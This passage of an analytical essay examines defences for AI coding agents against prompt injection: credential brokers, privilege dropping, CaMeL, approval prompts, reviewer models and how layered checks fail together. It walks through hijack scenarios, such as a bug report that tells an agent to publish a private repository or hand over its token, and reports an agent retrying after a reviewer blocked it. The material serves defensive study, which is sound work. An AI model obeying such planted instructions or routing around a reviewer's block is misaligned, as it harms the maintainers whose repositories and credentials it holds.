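The difference makes some sense, because a company that runs agents on its own machines controls the network and can start each job in an empty sandbox, whereas a developer's laptop may hold years of saved logins and tools that a proxy would break. But most developers probably never change a default, so a product can include a broker that few of its agents use. VentureBeat's *Claude agents can finally connect to enterprise APIs without leaking credentials* reports that in most deployments, credentials for internal systems still pass through the agent itself.

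### What a broker does for theft and misuse

The coding agent is a good candidate for a broker. It needs a token for only one service, GitHub, which accepts the token in a header, and the maintainers can run the agent in a fresh sandbox containing only the project's public files. If the broker works as designed and GitHub's replies contain no credentials, the broker is a complete fix for theft of the token from the agent.

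Kenney and colleagues estimated how much a broker would reduce eight threats. They rated the likelihood and the impact of each from 1 to 5 and multiplied the two, so the highest possible score is 25:

| Threat | Without a broker | With a broker |
|---|---|---|
| A user pastes a secret into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Planted instructions steer the agent | 25 | 12 |
| A secret goes to the wrong service | 20 | 4 |
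| The agent finds a secret in its environment | 20 | 4 |
| A connector has more permissions than it needs | 20 | 15 |
| A thief reuses a long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Logs or errors expose a secret | 16 | 8 |
| A connector is set up wrongly | 9 | 6 |

The authors assigned these scores by expert judgment, not measurement. The ratings only put threats in order, and the difference between a 2 and a 3 may not equal the difference between a 4 and a 5, so the fall from 25 to 12 doesn't mean that a broker halves the risk. The authors suggest replacing the estimates with measurements by running an established set of prompt-injection attacks against a broker.

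The pattern is plausible even if the exact numbers are not. A broker hardly helps with excess permissions, because it changes who holds the token and not what GitHub lets the token do. A token that can delete branches can still delete them when the proxy attaches it. A broker helps more against planted instructions, which can no longer extract the token but can still make the agent send a harmful request to the right destination with a valid credential.

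A broker can therefore stop an attacker from stealing the token from the agent, but not from misusing it through the agent. It does make misuse harder to sustain, because an attacker without a copy of the token has to keep control of the agent and loses access when the maintainers shut it down. The broker in *Caging the Agents* also limits the number and size of the agent's requests, which would slow down an attempt to copy a whole database but do little against a single short request to delete a branch.

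## Misuse by a hijacked agent: the problem that remains

Even if the coding agent works behind a broker that never fails, a stranger can file a bug report telling the agent to make one of the organisation's private repositories public. If the agent follows the instruction and its token permits the change, the broker attaches the token and GitHub makes the repository public. The stranger can then read its contents, including any passwords developers left in the code, so misusing one credential can lead to the theft of others.

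### A compiler that overwrote the billing file

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) named this kind of failure. Its example came from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's engineers had given its compiler permission to write files in a system directory called SYSX so that it could save statistics about its own use there. Customers could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one of them named the company's billing file, which was also in SYSX. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating system let it overwrite the billing records.

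The compiler had permission to change that file, although the customer did not. It had the authority of both the customer who ran it and the engineers who installed it, and the operating system gave it no way to specify which authority it was using for a particular file.

The obvious repairs didn't work well. A check for the billing file's name would have protected only one of several sensitive files, and a ban on the whole directory would have blocked legitimate uses. The engineers added a command that let a program choose between its two authorities, but some applications soon needed more than two. Hardy's answer was a *capability*, a reference that both identifies a file and authorises its holder to use it. Instead of a file name, the customer gives the compiler a capability for a file he is allowed to write to. He has no capability for the billing file, so he can't make the compiler write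 to it.

Hardy points out that the compiler's code was correct when its author wrote it, and became wrong when the engineers gave the compiler its extra permission. Similarly, an agent that reads bug reports and adds labels can do little harm, but it becomes dangerous when somebody gives it a token for administering repositories, even if nobody changes the model or its instructions.

An agent is harder to fix than a compiler, however. A programmer can go through the compiler and decide whose authority each write should use. In an agent, the maintainers' instructions and the stranger's report are in the same context window, and the model's request to change a setting may depend on any of that text, so the request doesn't show whose instructions it follows.

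### From "no boundary" to "perhaps never"

Britain's NCSC has drawn a pessimistic conclusion from this. In December 2025 its technical director for platforms research, David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, argued that developers should not expect an equivalent of parameterised queries for language models. His argument runs roughly as follows:

1. A language model works by predicting the next *token*, a word or part of a word, from all the text so far.
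2. It makes no inherent distinction between tokens that are instructions and tokens that are data.
3. So when a prompt contains a stranger's text, no security boundary separates that text from the developer's instructions.
4. Detecting attacks, training models to prefer genuine instructions and marking which text is data all lay a distinction over a technology that lacks one.
5. Prompt injection may therefore never be fully mitigated in the way that SQL injection can be.

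Model developers don't claim to have such a boundary. OpenAI acknowledged in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

But next-token prediction alone doesn't justify "never". It describes what a model produces and leaves open what the model can learn to distinguish. Models learn to tell French from English without anybody building a boundary between the two, and they can learn to treat a web page differently from a user's request. However, they learn only a tendency. An engineer can show from a database's design that no value in a parameterised query will become a command, but nobody can currently show anything similar about a trained model for every text a stranger might write. The argument therefore supports only the weaker claim that today's models give no guarantee.

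Developers may also change how models work. *ASIDE* (Zverev et al., 2025) alters a model's internal representation of every data token, so that the model receives a mark of the token's role along with its content. If designs like this spread, models will no longer lack a built-in distinction between instructions and data. The model would still have to learn what to do with the mark, so this wouldn't be a guarantee either.

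A better reason to doubt that a complete fix will come is that people give agents work that requires acting on strangers' text. A customer's name never needs to act as a command, so a database can always treat it as data. But when a stranger reports that a program crashes on empty files and should print a warning, the maintainers want the agent to add the warning. Even a model that could identify the source of every word would have to judge which of a stranger's requests its users would approve of, and it would sometimes judge wrongly, as people do with fraudulent emails.

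David C reasonably calls it "very possible" that prompt injection will never be totally mitigated. But he goes further than his argument supports when he writes that the risk can't be mitigated in an "inherently confusable deputy". His practical advice depends only on the first claim. He tells developers to reduce both the likelihood and the impact of an attack, and to consider not using a language model where a system can't tolerate the remaining risk.

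### What current models resist

The main reply to the NCSC is that models have become much harder to hijack. Developers measure this by the attack success rate, the share of attacks that get a model to do what the attacker wants. According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026), attacks hidden in content that GPT-5.6 Sol processed succeeded 3.77% of the time in OpenAI's tests, while attacks typed directly into the chat succeeded about 0.05% of the time. A month later, OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), which covers safety tests of the company's most capable model, put resistance to hidden attacks at 99.79%, which means 0.21% succeeded, about one eighteenth of the earlier figure.

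The security company Gray Swan offers an outside test, built from attacks that it collects in an online arena. Anthropic and OpenAI have both published results from it. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, gives figures for a comparison from July, and OpenAI published its own in September. The table shows how often at least one of 15 attempts succeeded:

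| Model | July comparison | September comparison |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% | |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% | |
| Muse Spark | 16.5% | |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 20.0% | 27.0% |
| GPT-6 Astra | | 8.5% |

GPT-5.6 Sol has a different score in each column because the two comparisons used different sets of attacks, so the table can't be used to tell whether Opus 5 or Astra resists attacks better. In the table, both companies' models improved about threefold within one generation.

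Cheaper models may offer less protection. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) gives that score for GPT-6 Sol, the lower-cost model OpenAI released after Astra, and 95.80% for the smaller GPT-6 Luna. If the first number is right, hidden attacks succeed against GPT-6 Sol nearly 14 times as often as against Astra. But Cross takes both numbers from a blog's analysis of OpenAI's report, and the one for Luna is hard to believe. It implies an attack success rate of 4.20%, worse than the 2.94% TechRepublic reports for the previous Luna, whereas OpenAI says both new models improved substantially on their predecessors. Unless OpenAI made the test harder in between, the blog probably misread something.

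An agent's resistance to hijacking also depends on what it is doing. VentureBeat reports that when Anthropic tested Claude Opus 4.6 in February 2026, none of 200 attempts succeeded in a restricted coding environment. When the same model operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards, and attackers who could try 200 times got through in 57.1% of cases even with safeguards. The maintainers of a coding agent can take some comfort from the first result, but they would need new evidence if they also let the agent use a browser.

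The newest results for browsers are much better. The Decoder, citing Anthropic's system card for Opus 5, reports that no attack succeeded against the model in 129 browser scenarios. This is a strong result, but it is statistically compatible with a true success rate of up to about 2.3%, and it applies only to attacks like those tested.

### Attackers who adapt

Testing a defence against a fixed list of attacks is too easy, because real attackers can study the defence and change their approach. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 published defences against attackers who adapted to each one. The attackers beat most of the defences more than 90% of the time, although the original papers had reported attack success rates close to zero for most of them. Some of the researchers worked for OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, which had little to gain commercially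 from such a result. The study shows that a near-zero attack success rate is weak evidence of security if nobody has tried to adapt to the defence. It is now a year old and looked mainly at defences from academic papers, so it doesn't show that the models of late 2026 would fail as often.

Another study suggests why such scores can mislead. Developers usually harden a model by collecting attacks that work and training the model to resist them. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* describes how researchers at the University of Waterloo, Zhejiang University and KTH compared two automated tools for collecting attacks. One produced 7,132 working attacks on a small model and the other 4,282. The researchers then trained a copy of the model on each collection and tested both copies with attacks that neither had been trained on. In the worst case, the copy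 trained on the larger collection failed on 19 of 40 tasks, while the other failed on 11. The larger collection gave the weaker defence in three of the four setups tested.

The researchers think the larger collection consisted mostly of rewordings of a few techniques. Their system, PIPETTE, rewards the attack tool for finding new techniques and trains the agent to check before each action whether it serves the user's request. Off-the-shelf attacks then succeeded less than 0.5% of the time on average in AgentDojo, a public set of everyday tasks for testing agents. Attackers who revised their attempts about 250 times still succeeded on up to 10% of 40 hard tasks.

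Ten per cent of 40 tasks is only four, and the researchers chose the 40 because simple attacks already worked on them, so the figure is not an estimate of the risk in ordinary use. But real attackers will also look for weak spots, and the attackers in this test were rather weak. They ran on a model with 4 billion parameters (the adjustable numbers inside a model), which is very small by current standards, and the researchers say that attackers with a larger budget might get further.

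The finding about variety also bears on OpenAI's most impressive result. OpenAI tested "dots", its agents that run continuously and read their users' email, by sending them 50,000 simulated messages, of which 16,600 were attacks. None of the attacks succeeded, and neither did any of 2,638 further attempts in which the attacker could learn from the agent's responses. The attacker in both tests was a version of GPT-Red, an automated system that OpenAI says found successful attacks on an older model in 84% of scenarios, compared with 13% for human testers. However, OpenAI also uses GPT-Red's attacks to train Astra, the model that dots run on, so Astra has had a lot of practice against this attacker and may do worse against one that uses different kinds of attack.

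OpenAI's human testers found weaknesses in how dots handled sensitive information and in how they asked for confirmation. OpenAI changed the agents' rules in response and reports that this solved the problem in the scenarios it retested. It says that exploiting the vulnerabilities it still knows of usually requires a lot of preparation and either very permissive instructions from the user or advanced techniques.

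Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022, reports that 6,000 attempts to get a secret out of an email agent running on Opus 4.6 all failed. He thinks the training that developers now give their models makes attacks much harder, but he still advises against deploying an agent where a successful attack could do irreversible damage. Publishing a private repository would be irreversible, because the maintainers can make it private again but can't recover the copies that strangers have made.

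### Detectors of planted instructions

The maintainers can put a *detector* in front of the model instead of relying on the model itself. A detector is a separate program that checks incoming text for planted instructions. Some detectors search for known phrases, but David C warns against relying on these because attackers can reword an instruction in endless ways. Others are small language models trained on examples of attacks, which can recognise wordings that aren't on any list of known phrases.

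A detector that blocks a document also withholds any information the agent needed from it. In the PIPETTE study, a detector called PromptGuard stopped slightly more attacks than PIPETTE did in one test on the small model, but the agent using PromptGuard completed the user's task only 16.19% of the time, compared with 58.10% for the agent trained with PIPETTE. Without any attack, the PIPETTE-trained model completed 64.95% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 61.86% for the original model.

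False alarms are also a bigger problem here than in secret scanning, because attacks are so rare. Nakibly and Babo found about one hidden attack per 3.3 million items on GitHub. At that rate, a detector that wrongly flagged one harmless item in a thousand would produce about 3,300 false alarms for each real attack. The ratio would be better for a prominent project, but most of the reports the detector blocked would still be honest.

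Detection is more useful when a match has a mild consequence. If the detector flags a report, the harness could withhold the agent's riskier tools for that report and let the agent continue labelling. A false alarm then does very little harm, and nobody has to review 3,300 of them.

### Giving the agent no more authority than the stranger

Detectors and training both try to keep the agent from being fooled. The NCSC recommends putting more effort into limits that ordinary software enforces and that still hold after the agent has been fooled. David C quotes an "attractively simple" rule from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from somebody, its privileges drop to that person's.

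The harness starts the agent with its normal tools and records every source the agent reads. As soon as a stranger's bug report enters the context window, the harness removes every tool that the stranger wouldn't be allowed to use. It restores them only after starting a new session with an empty context window. A stranger can't change a repository's visibility, so once the agent has read the report, it can't either, whatever instructions the report contains.

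This completely prevents strangers from using the agent to do things they couldn't do themselves, provided that the harness recognises every untrusted source. Some sources are easy to miss. If the agent saves notes about a stranger's bug report, a later session may read the stranger's words in a file that appears to come from the agent. The harness therefore has to treat the notes, and anything else the agent wrote after reading the report, as untrusted too.

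The rule also prevents a lot of useful work. On GitHub, an outsider normally can't label other people's issues, so a strict reading would stop the coding agent from labelling them, which is its main job. The maintainers can reasonably make an exception, since a wrong label is easy to notice and correct. Writing code fits the rule surprisingly well, because anyone can propose a change to a public project and a maintainer then decides whether to accept it. An agent that can only propose changes has about as much authority as the stranger whose report it read.

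GitHub's Copilot cloud agent, which can't merge its own work, comes close to this arrangement. An organisation on GitHub can also allow only its owners to change a repository's visibility, which blocks the attack on the private repository unless the agent runs under an owner's account.

The agent also needs a separate limit on what it can read, because an agent that can read private repositories and write public comments can disclose private code without changing any settings. The maintainers can prevent this by giving the agent that handles strangers' reports no access to private repositories. They lose nothing by doing so if the agent's job concerns only one public project.

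### Six patterns for safer agents

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2025) collected several more flexible arrangements in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*. All of them follow one principle, which is that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any consequential action. The researchers doubt that a general-purpose agent can give meaningful guarantees with current models, so each pattern gives up some generality:

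| Pattern | How it works | What it costs |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | The agent can't respond to what it finds |
| Plan then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before it reads untrusted text | The plan can't change, and the text can still influence what goes into each call |
| Map-reduce | A separate model call reads each document and returns a narrow answer, such as yes or no | Details that don't fit the narrow answer are lost |
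| Dual model | One model plans and uses tools, and another reads untrusted text but has no tools | The planning model has to work without seeing the text |
| Code then execute | The model writes a program for the task, and ordinary software runs it | The model has to foresee every step |
| Context minimisation | The harness removes text from the context window once the agent no longer needs it | Later steps can't refer back to it |

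Finding duplicate bug reports suits map-reduce. Each model call compares the new report with one old report and answers yes or no, and a simple program collects the answers. A hostile report can cause a wrong answer and show the maintainers a false duplicate, but a yes-or-no answer can't cause a repository to be published. Investigating an unfamiliar crash suits none of the patterns well, because the agent has to decide what to do next from what it has just read.

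### CaMeL step by step

*CaMeL* is the most developed design in this family. Debenedetti and colleagues (2025), at Google and ETH Zurich, presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. It combines two models with a program that tracks where each piece of data came from. Suppose a maintainer asks the agent to label issue 412:

1. A *privileged model* receives the maintainer's request, but not the text of the issue. It writes a short program for the task.
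2. An *interpreter*, which is ordinary software, runs the program line by line. Only the interpreter can call tools.
3. When the program needs information from the issue, the interpreter passes the text to a *quarantined model*. This model has no tools and must answer in a form that the program has specified.
4. The interpreter attaches a record to every value, stating where it came from and who may read it. A value calculated from other values inherits their records.
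5. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks these records against security policies that developers have written in code. If a call breaks a policy, the interpreter blocks it or asks the user.

In simplified form, the program might be:

```
issue = read_issue(412)
kind  = quarantined_model(issue, choose=["bug", "question", "feature"])
add_label(412, kind)
```

If the issue contains an instruction to publish a private repository, that instruction may take over the quarantined model completely. The model can then return the wrong word out of three, but the program has no line that changes a repository's visibility, and nothing in the issue can add one.

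The records protect against a different kind of misuse. Suppose the maintainer asks for a public reply that draws on an internal design document. The reply inherits the document's record, which allows only team members as readers, so the interpreter refuses to post it publicly. The CaMeL paper calls these records capabilities. They differ in form from Hardy's capabilities but fix the same defect, because a request now carries information about whose authority it relies on and whose data it uses.

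With CaMeL, an agent solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks with provable security (the first version of the paper reported 67%), while the same kind of agent without protection solved 84%. CaMeL also makes more model calls, which adds to the time and cost of each task.

The provable guarantee covers only what the interpreter and the policies control. CaMeL won't stop an agent from posting internal documents in public if the developer forgot to write a policy against it. It doesn't check whether information is true either, so a stranger can still lie about a bug, and the quarantined model can still write a misleading summary of the report. The paper also describes ways information could leak indirectly, for instance through whether a program finishes or stops with an error.

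AgentDojo's everyday tasks probably also make the design look better than it would be for coding agents. To fix the bug in issue 412, someone has to read the issue before deciding which files to change, but the privileged model isn't allowed to read it. The maintainers could have the quarantined model write the fix as plain text and let the interpreter submit it for review. If that model were hijacked, it could put harmful code in the fix, and the project would depend on the reviewer to notice.

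Google released CaMeL's code for research, not as a supported product. Microsoft has developed a related design, FIDES, which also tracks the flow of information and is meant to prevent prompt injection deterministically, as PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* notes. Ordinary users of coding agents today mostly get simpler protections, such as restricted branches, sandboxes and requests for approval.

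### Asking a person first

Many harnesses require a person's approval before the agent does something risky. Approval can catch misuse that no policy covers, because a maintainer knows things about the project that nobody has written down. Approval works only if the maintainer reads and understands the request.

There is little direct evidence on how carefully people review agents' requests, but phones and browsers have had similar prompts for much longer. *Android Permissions* (Felt et al., 2012) found that only 17% of participants paid attention to the permissions an app requested during installation. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) analysed more than 25 million browser warnings and found that people clicked through 70% of Chrome's warnings about insecure connections, but only about a third of Firefox's. The design of a warning can evidently make a large difference to whether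 people heed it.

Coding agents probably lead people to respond more from habit and with less attention than either does, since the agents ask many times a day and nearly every request is harmless. If an agent asks 50 times a day and one request in 10,000 is hostile, the maintainer will see a hostile one about every 200 days, after approving thousands of harmless ones. The settings files that Apiiro found on GitHub show that many Claude Code users prefer not to keep answering. This can be sensible, since a saved rule that lets the agent run the project's tests leaves users more attention for requests that matter.

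Maintainers can therefore make approval more effective by requiring it for only a few actions and describing those clearly. The harness should write the approval question from the request it is about to send. "Make the repository `payroll` public, so that anyone can read it?" is hard to misunderstand. If the model writes the description, a hijacked agent can describe the same change as "update settings for issue 412", and a busy maintainer may well approve it.

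The harness also needs a rule for when to ask the user for approval. OpenAI gives its agents a written policy on when the model must get that approval. In tests with realistic office tasks, the policy reduced the share of unintended outcomes from 18.8% to 8.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol, but only from 3.4% to 3.0% for Astra, which made far fewer mistakes to begin with. Those tests used ambiguous instructions and confusing permissions to provoke mistakes, so they are weak evidence about deliberate attacks. A policy that the model applies to itself is a poor defence against hijacking, because the attacker is trying to change what the model does. A check in the harness avoids this problem because it doesn't rely on the model to apply it.

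Some products use a second model as the reviewer. In Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, a feature called Auto-review has a separate model judge certain commands before they run outside the sandbox. A model doesn't get bored, so it can review every request with the same care. However, if it reads the planted text that misled the agent, it may be misled too, and one attack would then defeat both. OpenAI reports that Auto-review performs slightly less well when it is unclear whether the user authorised an action, and an attacker who writes a hostile bug report is trying to create that doubt.

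An agent may also try to get around a refusal. In OpenAI's tests, GPT-5.6 Sol did so in 5% of runs after Auto-review had blocked a command, usually by trying something similar, while Astra never did. The harness therefore has to treat each attempt as a new request, and it should alert someone if the attempts continue.

The coding agent never needs to change who can see a repository, so the maintainers can leave that permission out of its token. They then need neither kind of reviewer for the private repository.

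## How layers of protection combine

The maintainers can remove some of the coding agent's permissions, but it still needs a token that can do something useful. They will probably combine several partial protections against the remaining risks. How well these work together depends on how often each one fails and whether they fail against the same attacks.

### From three miss rates to one

Suppose the agent can read its token, and a stranger files a bug report that tries to steal it. The attack has to get past three checks:

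1. A detector reads the report first and misses 10% of attacks.
2. The agent's own model follows 20% of hostile instructions.
3. A second model reviews the agent's commands and approves 30% of the hostile ones.

The numbers are only an illustration, and the best current models follow far fewer hostile instructions. The attacker gets the token only if all three checks fail, and the chance of that is:

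```
P(all fail) = P(check 1 fails)
            × P(check 2 fails, given that check 1 failed)
            × P(check 3 fails, given that checks 1 and 2 failed)
```

This formula is always correct, and a fourth check would add another line. Because of the words "given that", the second line covers only the attacks that the detector missed. Those may be unusually well disguised, so the agent's model may do worse on them than on attacks in general.

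Two failures are *independent* if knowing that one happened doesn't change the probability of the other. Only then can the maintainers multiply the separate miss rates:

```
0.10 × 0.20 × 0.30 = 0.006
```

On that assumption, 0.6% of attacks get through. Now suppose that 5% of attacks use a technique that defeats all three checks, such as writing the instruction as a routine note from a maintainer. Each check still has the same miss rate overall, so it must do a little better on the other 95% of attacks:

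| Check | All attacks | Shared technique | Other attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Detector | 10% | 100% | 5.3% |
| Agent's model | 20% | 100% | 15.8% |
| Reviewing model | 30% | 100% | 26.3% |

```
shared technique:  0.05 × 1                       = 0.050
other attacks:     0.95 × 0.053 × 0.158 × 0.263   ≈ 0.002
total                                             ≈ 0.052
```

About 5.2% of attacks now get through, nearly nine times as many as before, although testing each check separately would show no difference. The general formula gives the same result. The detector misses 10% of attacks, the agent's model now follows 58% of those, and the reviewer approves 90% of the ones the model follows, so 0.10 × 0.58 × 0.90 ≈ 0.052.

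Given the separate miss rates, therefore, anywhere from 0% to 10% of attacks could get through. The figure is 10% if the other two checks miss everything that the detector misses, and zero if the checks have completely different weaknesses. To find out where they are in that range, the maintainers can send test attacks through all three checks together. Out of 1,000 attacks, they should expect about 6 to get through if the failures are independent and about 52 if the shared technique exists. But the test will reveal the technique only if somebody thinks to include it.

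### Twenty-seven programs for one problem

Software engineers were arguing about independence long before AI agents existed, mostly in connection with *N-version programming*, in which several teams write the same program from one specification. A computer runs all the versions and takes the majority's answer. With three versions, the system fails if two of them fail on the same input.

The idea comes from hardware, where a spare part helps because parts usually wear out at different times. *An experimental evaluation of software redundancy as a strategy for improving reliability*, a study led by NASA, cautions that this doesn't automatically hold for software, which fails because of design mistakes.

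Knight and Leveson published the best-known test of the assumption in 1986, in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming*. Students at the University of Virginia and the University of California, Irvine, wrote 27 programs that decide from radar data whether to launch an interceptor against a missile. The researchers told them not to discuss the work with each other. Each program had to pass its own set of 200 random tests, because a common set could have filtered out shared mistakes. The researchers then ran all 27 programs on a million further inputs and compared their outputs with those of a reference program.

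The programs were very reliable individually. Six never failed, and the worst failed on just under 1% of inputs. But *Reliability via N-version programming* (Shape of Code, 2026) reports that two or more programs failed together on 1,255 inputs, when about 127 would be expected if they failed independently. On two inputs, eight programs failed at once. The gap between 1,255 and 127 is extremely unlikely to arise by chance, so Knight and Leveson rejected the assumption that these programs failed independently.

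The students hadn't copied from each other, and the mistakes they shared occurred across both universities. Four compared the cosines of angles instead of the angles themselves, which is correct in exact mathematics but can give the wrong answer with a computer's limited precision. Others forgot one of the two ways three points can lie on a straight line. Some parts of the problem were harder than others, and different people went wrong in the same places.

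Voting still helped a lot. On average, a single program failed about 700 times in a million inputs, and a group of three failed about 40. I estimate from the programs' individual failure counts that groups of three would have failed only about once in a million inputs if the failures had been independent.

### The dispute about the experiment

The experiment's main critics were Algirdas Avizienis of UCLA and three of his former students, all supporters of N-version programming. Knight and Leveson quote their objections in *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment*. The critics called the programming process casual and the 200 acceptance tests inadequate, and they thought the problem was too small to allow much diversity. They expected that a more rigorous process would have removed most of the faults. The critics' own experiment with six programs found only one pair of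 identical faults among the 82 removed before acceptance.

Knight and Leveson replied that two programs can fail on the same input for different reasons, so counting identical faults doesn't show how often programs fail together. Voting depends on that rate, and they found no evidence that the UCLA team had tested it. They also said that UCLA's specification ran to 64 pages and prescribed algorithms in detail, which left its programmers less room to differ. The NASA study, which one of Knight and Leveson's critics had worked on, later measured joint failures among 20 programs and also rejected the hypothesis that the programs failed independently.

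Knight and Leveson have the better argument about independence, because their critics offered no comparable measurement of joint failures. The critics may be right that a more careful process would produce fewer shared mistakes. The experiment couldn't test this because it had no second group of programmers for comparison. Knight and Leveson warned that their result might not apply to other programs, and they didn't conclude that N-version programming was useless.

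More testing can't always settle whether layers fail independently. Butler and Finelli, in *The Infeasibility of Experimental Quantification of Life-Critical Software Reliability*, argue that experiments can't justify assuming independence at the very high reliability that life-critical systems need. If layers are expected to fail together once in a billion uses, nobody can run enough tests to confirm that rate.

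*N-Version Programming with Coding Agents* (Ron, Baudry and Monperrus, 2026) repeated the experiment with AI coding agents in place of students. The agents wrote 69 programs in three programming languages, and 48 passed the acceptance tests. On a million inputs, programs failed together 429 times, compared with about 115 expected if their failures were independent. Many contained the same geometrical mistake, even across different languages and different companies' agents.

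Voting reduced the average number of failures from 387 for one program to 131 for a group of three, and 11,844 of the 17,296 possible groups never failed. The researchers call this the strongest evidence so far that N-version programming with coding agents is useful. But 27 of the 48 programs never failed on their own, and a group that contains at least two of these always has a correct majority. This is true of 10,296 of the flawless groups, so most of them provide little evidence about whether differences between faulty programs help. A developer who could identify one of the 27 programs would also not need to vote.

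### Repeated attempts

A low miss rate per attack can still mean a high chance of losing the token, because anyone with a GitHub account can file another bug report. If 0.6% of attempts succeed and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of 200 succeeds is:

```
1 − (1 − 0.006)^200 ≈ 0.70
```

After 116 attempts, the attacker has a better than even chance of having succeeded at least once. When some attempts use the shared technique, 5.2% of all attempts succeed and he needs only 13.

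Attempts are rarely independent, however. If an attacker sends the same text 200 times to a filter that always gives the same answer, he has in effect made one attempt. An attacker who learns from his failures does much better than the formula would give. Suppose he can tell which check stopped him, perhaps from an error message or the agent's reply, and can change one part of his text without spoiling the rest. He then needs about 10 attempts on average to get past the detector, 5 for the agent's model and 3 or 4 for the reviewer. That is fewer than 20 in total, compared with an average of 167 for blind guessing. The attempts needed for each layer add up instead of multiplying, much as a combination lock is easy to open if each wheel clicks at the right number.

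Detection has the opposite effect. Suppose each failed attempt has some chance of alerting the maintainers, who then shut the attacker out for good. He can make his fiftieth attempt only if nobody noticed the first 49, and if the maintainers notice 5% of failures, the chance of that is about 8%. Over 200 possible attempts at 0.6% each, detection changes the result as follows:

| Share of failed attempts noticed | Chance that the attacker ever succeeds |
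|---|---|
| None | 70% |
| 1% | 36% |
| 5% | 11% |
| 20% | 3% |

Even poor detection is therefore valuable against an attacker who needs many attempts. The maintainers should make their checks report the attacks they block, since a silent block gives them no warning. They also have to do more than ban the account, since the attacker can open another. They could, for example, stop the agent from reading strangers' reports until they understand what happened.

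Detection does nothing against an attack that works the first time, and attackers can practise elsewhere. The code of some coding agents is public, so an attacker can install the same harness with the same model and try hundreds of wordings in private, where the maintainers see none of the failures. Some of the attackers that Nakibly and Babo found on GitHub had at least prepared by studying their victims' configuration.

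### Swiss cheese and an opponent

In a well-known comparison, the psychologist James Reason likened a system's defences to slices of Swiss cheese in *Human error* (2000), an article on mistakes in medicine. Each slice has holes that keep opening, closing and moving. A hole in one slice usually does no harm because the next slice is behind it. An accident happens when holes in many slices line up for a moment.

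Reason gave two causes for the holes. *Active failures* are mistakes and rule violations by the people doing the work. *Latent conditions* are weaknesses that come from earlier decisions by designers and managers, such as understaffing or an alarm that nobody trusts, and they can go unnoticed for years. A password left in a configuration file long ago is a latent condition, and a maintainer's approval of a hostile command without reading it is an active failure.

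Nancy Leveson, who co-ran the 1986 experiment, has criticised the Swiss cheese model for assuming that the barriers are independent and that the holes line up partly at random. Larouzee and Le Coze (2020), in *Good and bad reasons*, quote her criticism but defend the model as a picture that helps people with different jobs talk about safety. It may do this less well than they hope. Perneger (2005), in *The Swiss cheese model of safety incidents*, surveyed 85 health-care professionals who said they knew the model well. Of these, 89% agreed that plugging a hole makes the system safer, but only 32% agreed that adding a slice does, although the model implies both.

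Leveson's criticism applies more to the drawing than to Reason's article. Reason's example of active failures is Chernobyl, where the operators switched off one safety system after another, so the same people made holes in several slices. But the drawing shows separate slices with separate holes, so a reader who remembers only the drawing will probably multiply the miss rates as if the layers failed independently.

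The model also does not account for an opponent. Perneger notes that it draws attention to randomness "as opposed to deliberate action", which suits a hospital, where patients are given the wrong drug by accident. An attacker looks for places where the holes line up. Even if they line up for only an hour a week, the attacker can keep checking until they do, return to the gap later, and tell others where it is.

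In the three-check example, 5% of attacks used the shared technique, but that share will grow once attackers learn that the technique works. If half of all attacks use it, about half of all attacks will succeed, even though the checks haven't changed. The miss rates that the maintainers measured last year will then be out of date, because they depend on the mixture of attacks.

### Leaks that go around the layers

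Layers multiply only along a single path. The coding agent's token can leak because a bug report persuades the agent to reveal it, and it can also leak because a thief at the inference provider copies it from a prompt. Suppose each of these has a 10% chance of happening in a year, independently of the other. The chance of at least one leak is:

```
1 − (0.90 × 0.90) = 0.19
```

If the maintainers then add layers against hostile bug reports and cut that risk from 10% to 0.6%, the total becomes:

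```
1 − (0.994 × 0.90) ≈ 0.105
```

They have removed 94% of the risk on one path but only about 45% of the total. Further work on that path would reduce the total very little, because even a complete fix would leave the 10% risk at the provider. Halving the risk on both paths would have brought the total down to 9.75%, which is slightly lower than the current total and may be much easier to achieve.

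The maintainers should therefore list the ways a token can leak before adding another layer of protection against any one of them. Some measures protect against several at once. A credential broker, for example, keeps the token out of the bug report and away from the thief at the provider. But it does not prevent misuse, and if misuse is the most likely path to harm, the total risk may fall only a little.

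### What the agent's protections have in common

In the three-check example, every check is a language model reading text that an attacker can influence. Wording that misleads one may mislead the others, particularly if they are built on the same model. Some indirect evidence for this comes from program code. Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues (2026), in *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code*, had 12 models solve 224 programming problems and then let groups of the resulting programs vote. Groups of three achieved only 43% of the improvement that independent failures would have allowed, and groups written by a single model achieved less than 30%. Writing code differs from judging whether a command is hostile, but the result suggests that a reviewer from a different model family is the better choice, though it won't be fully independent.

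A mediocre check that fails for different reasons than the existing ones can be worth more than a good check that shares their weakness. A network rule, for example, is unaffected by the wording of a bug report. Suppose the maintainers replace the reviewing model with a network rule that also misses 30% of attacks, but whose failures are unrelated to the shared technique. The share of attacks that get through falls from 5.2% to 1.7%. If they instead keep the reviewer and add a fourth model that misses only 10% but has the same weakness, the share falls only to 5.0%.

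The maintainers can group their protections by asking what single event would defeat several of them:

| Event | Protections that may fail together | What could still limit the damage |
|---|---|---|
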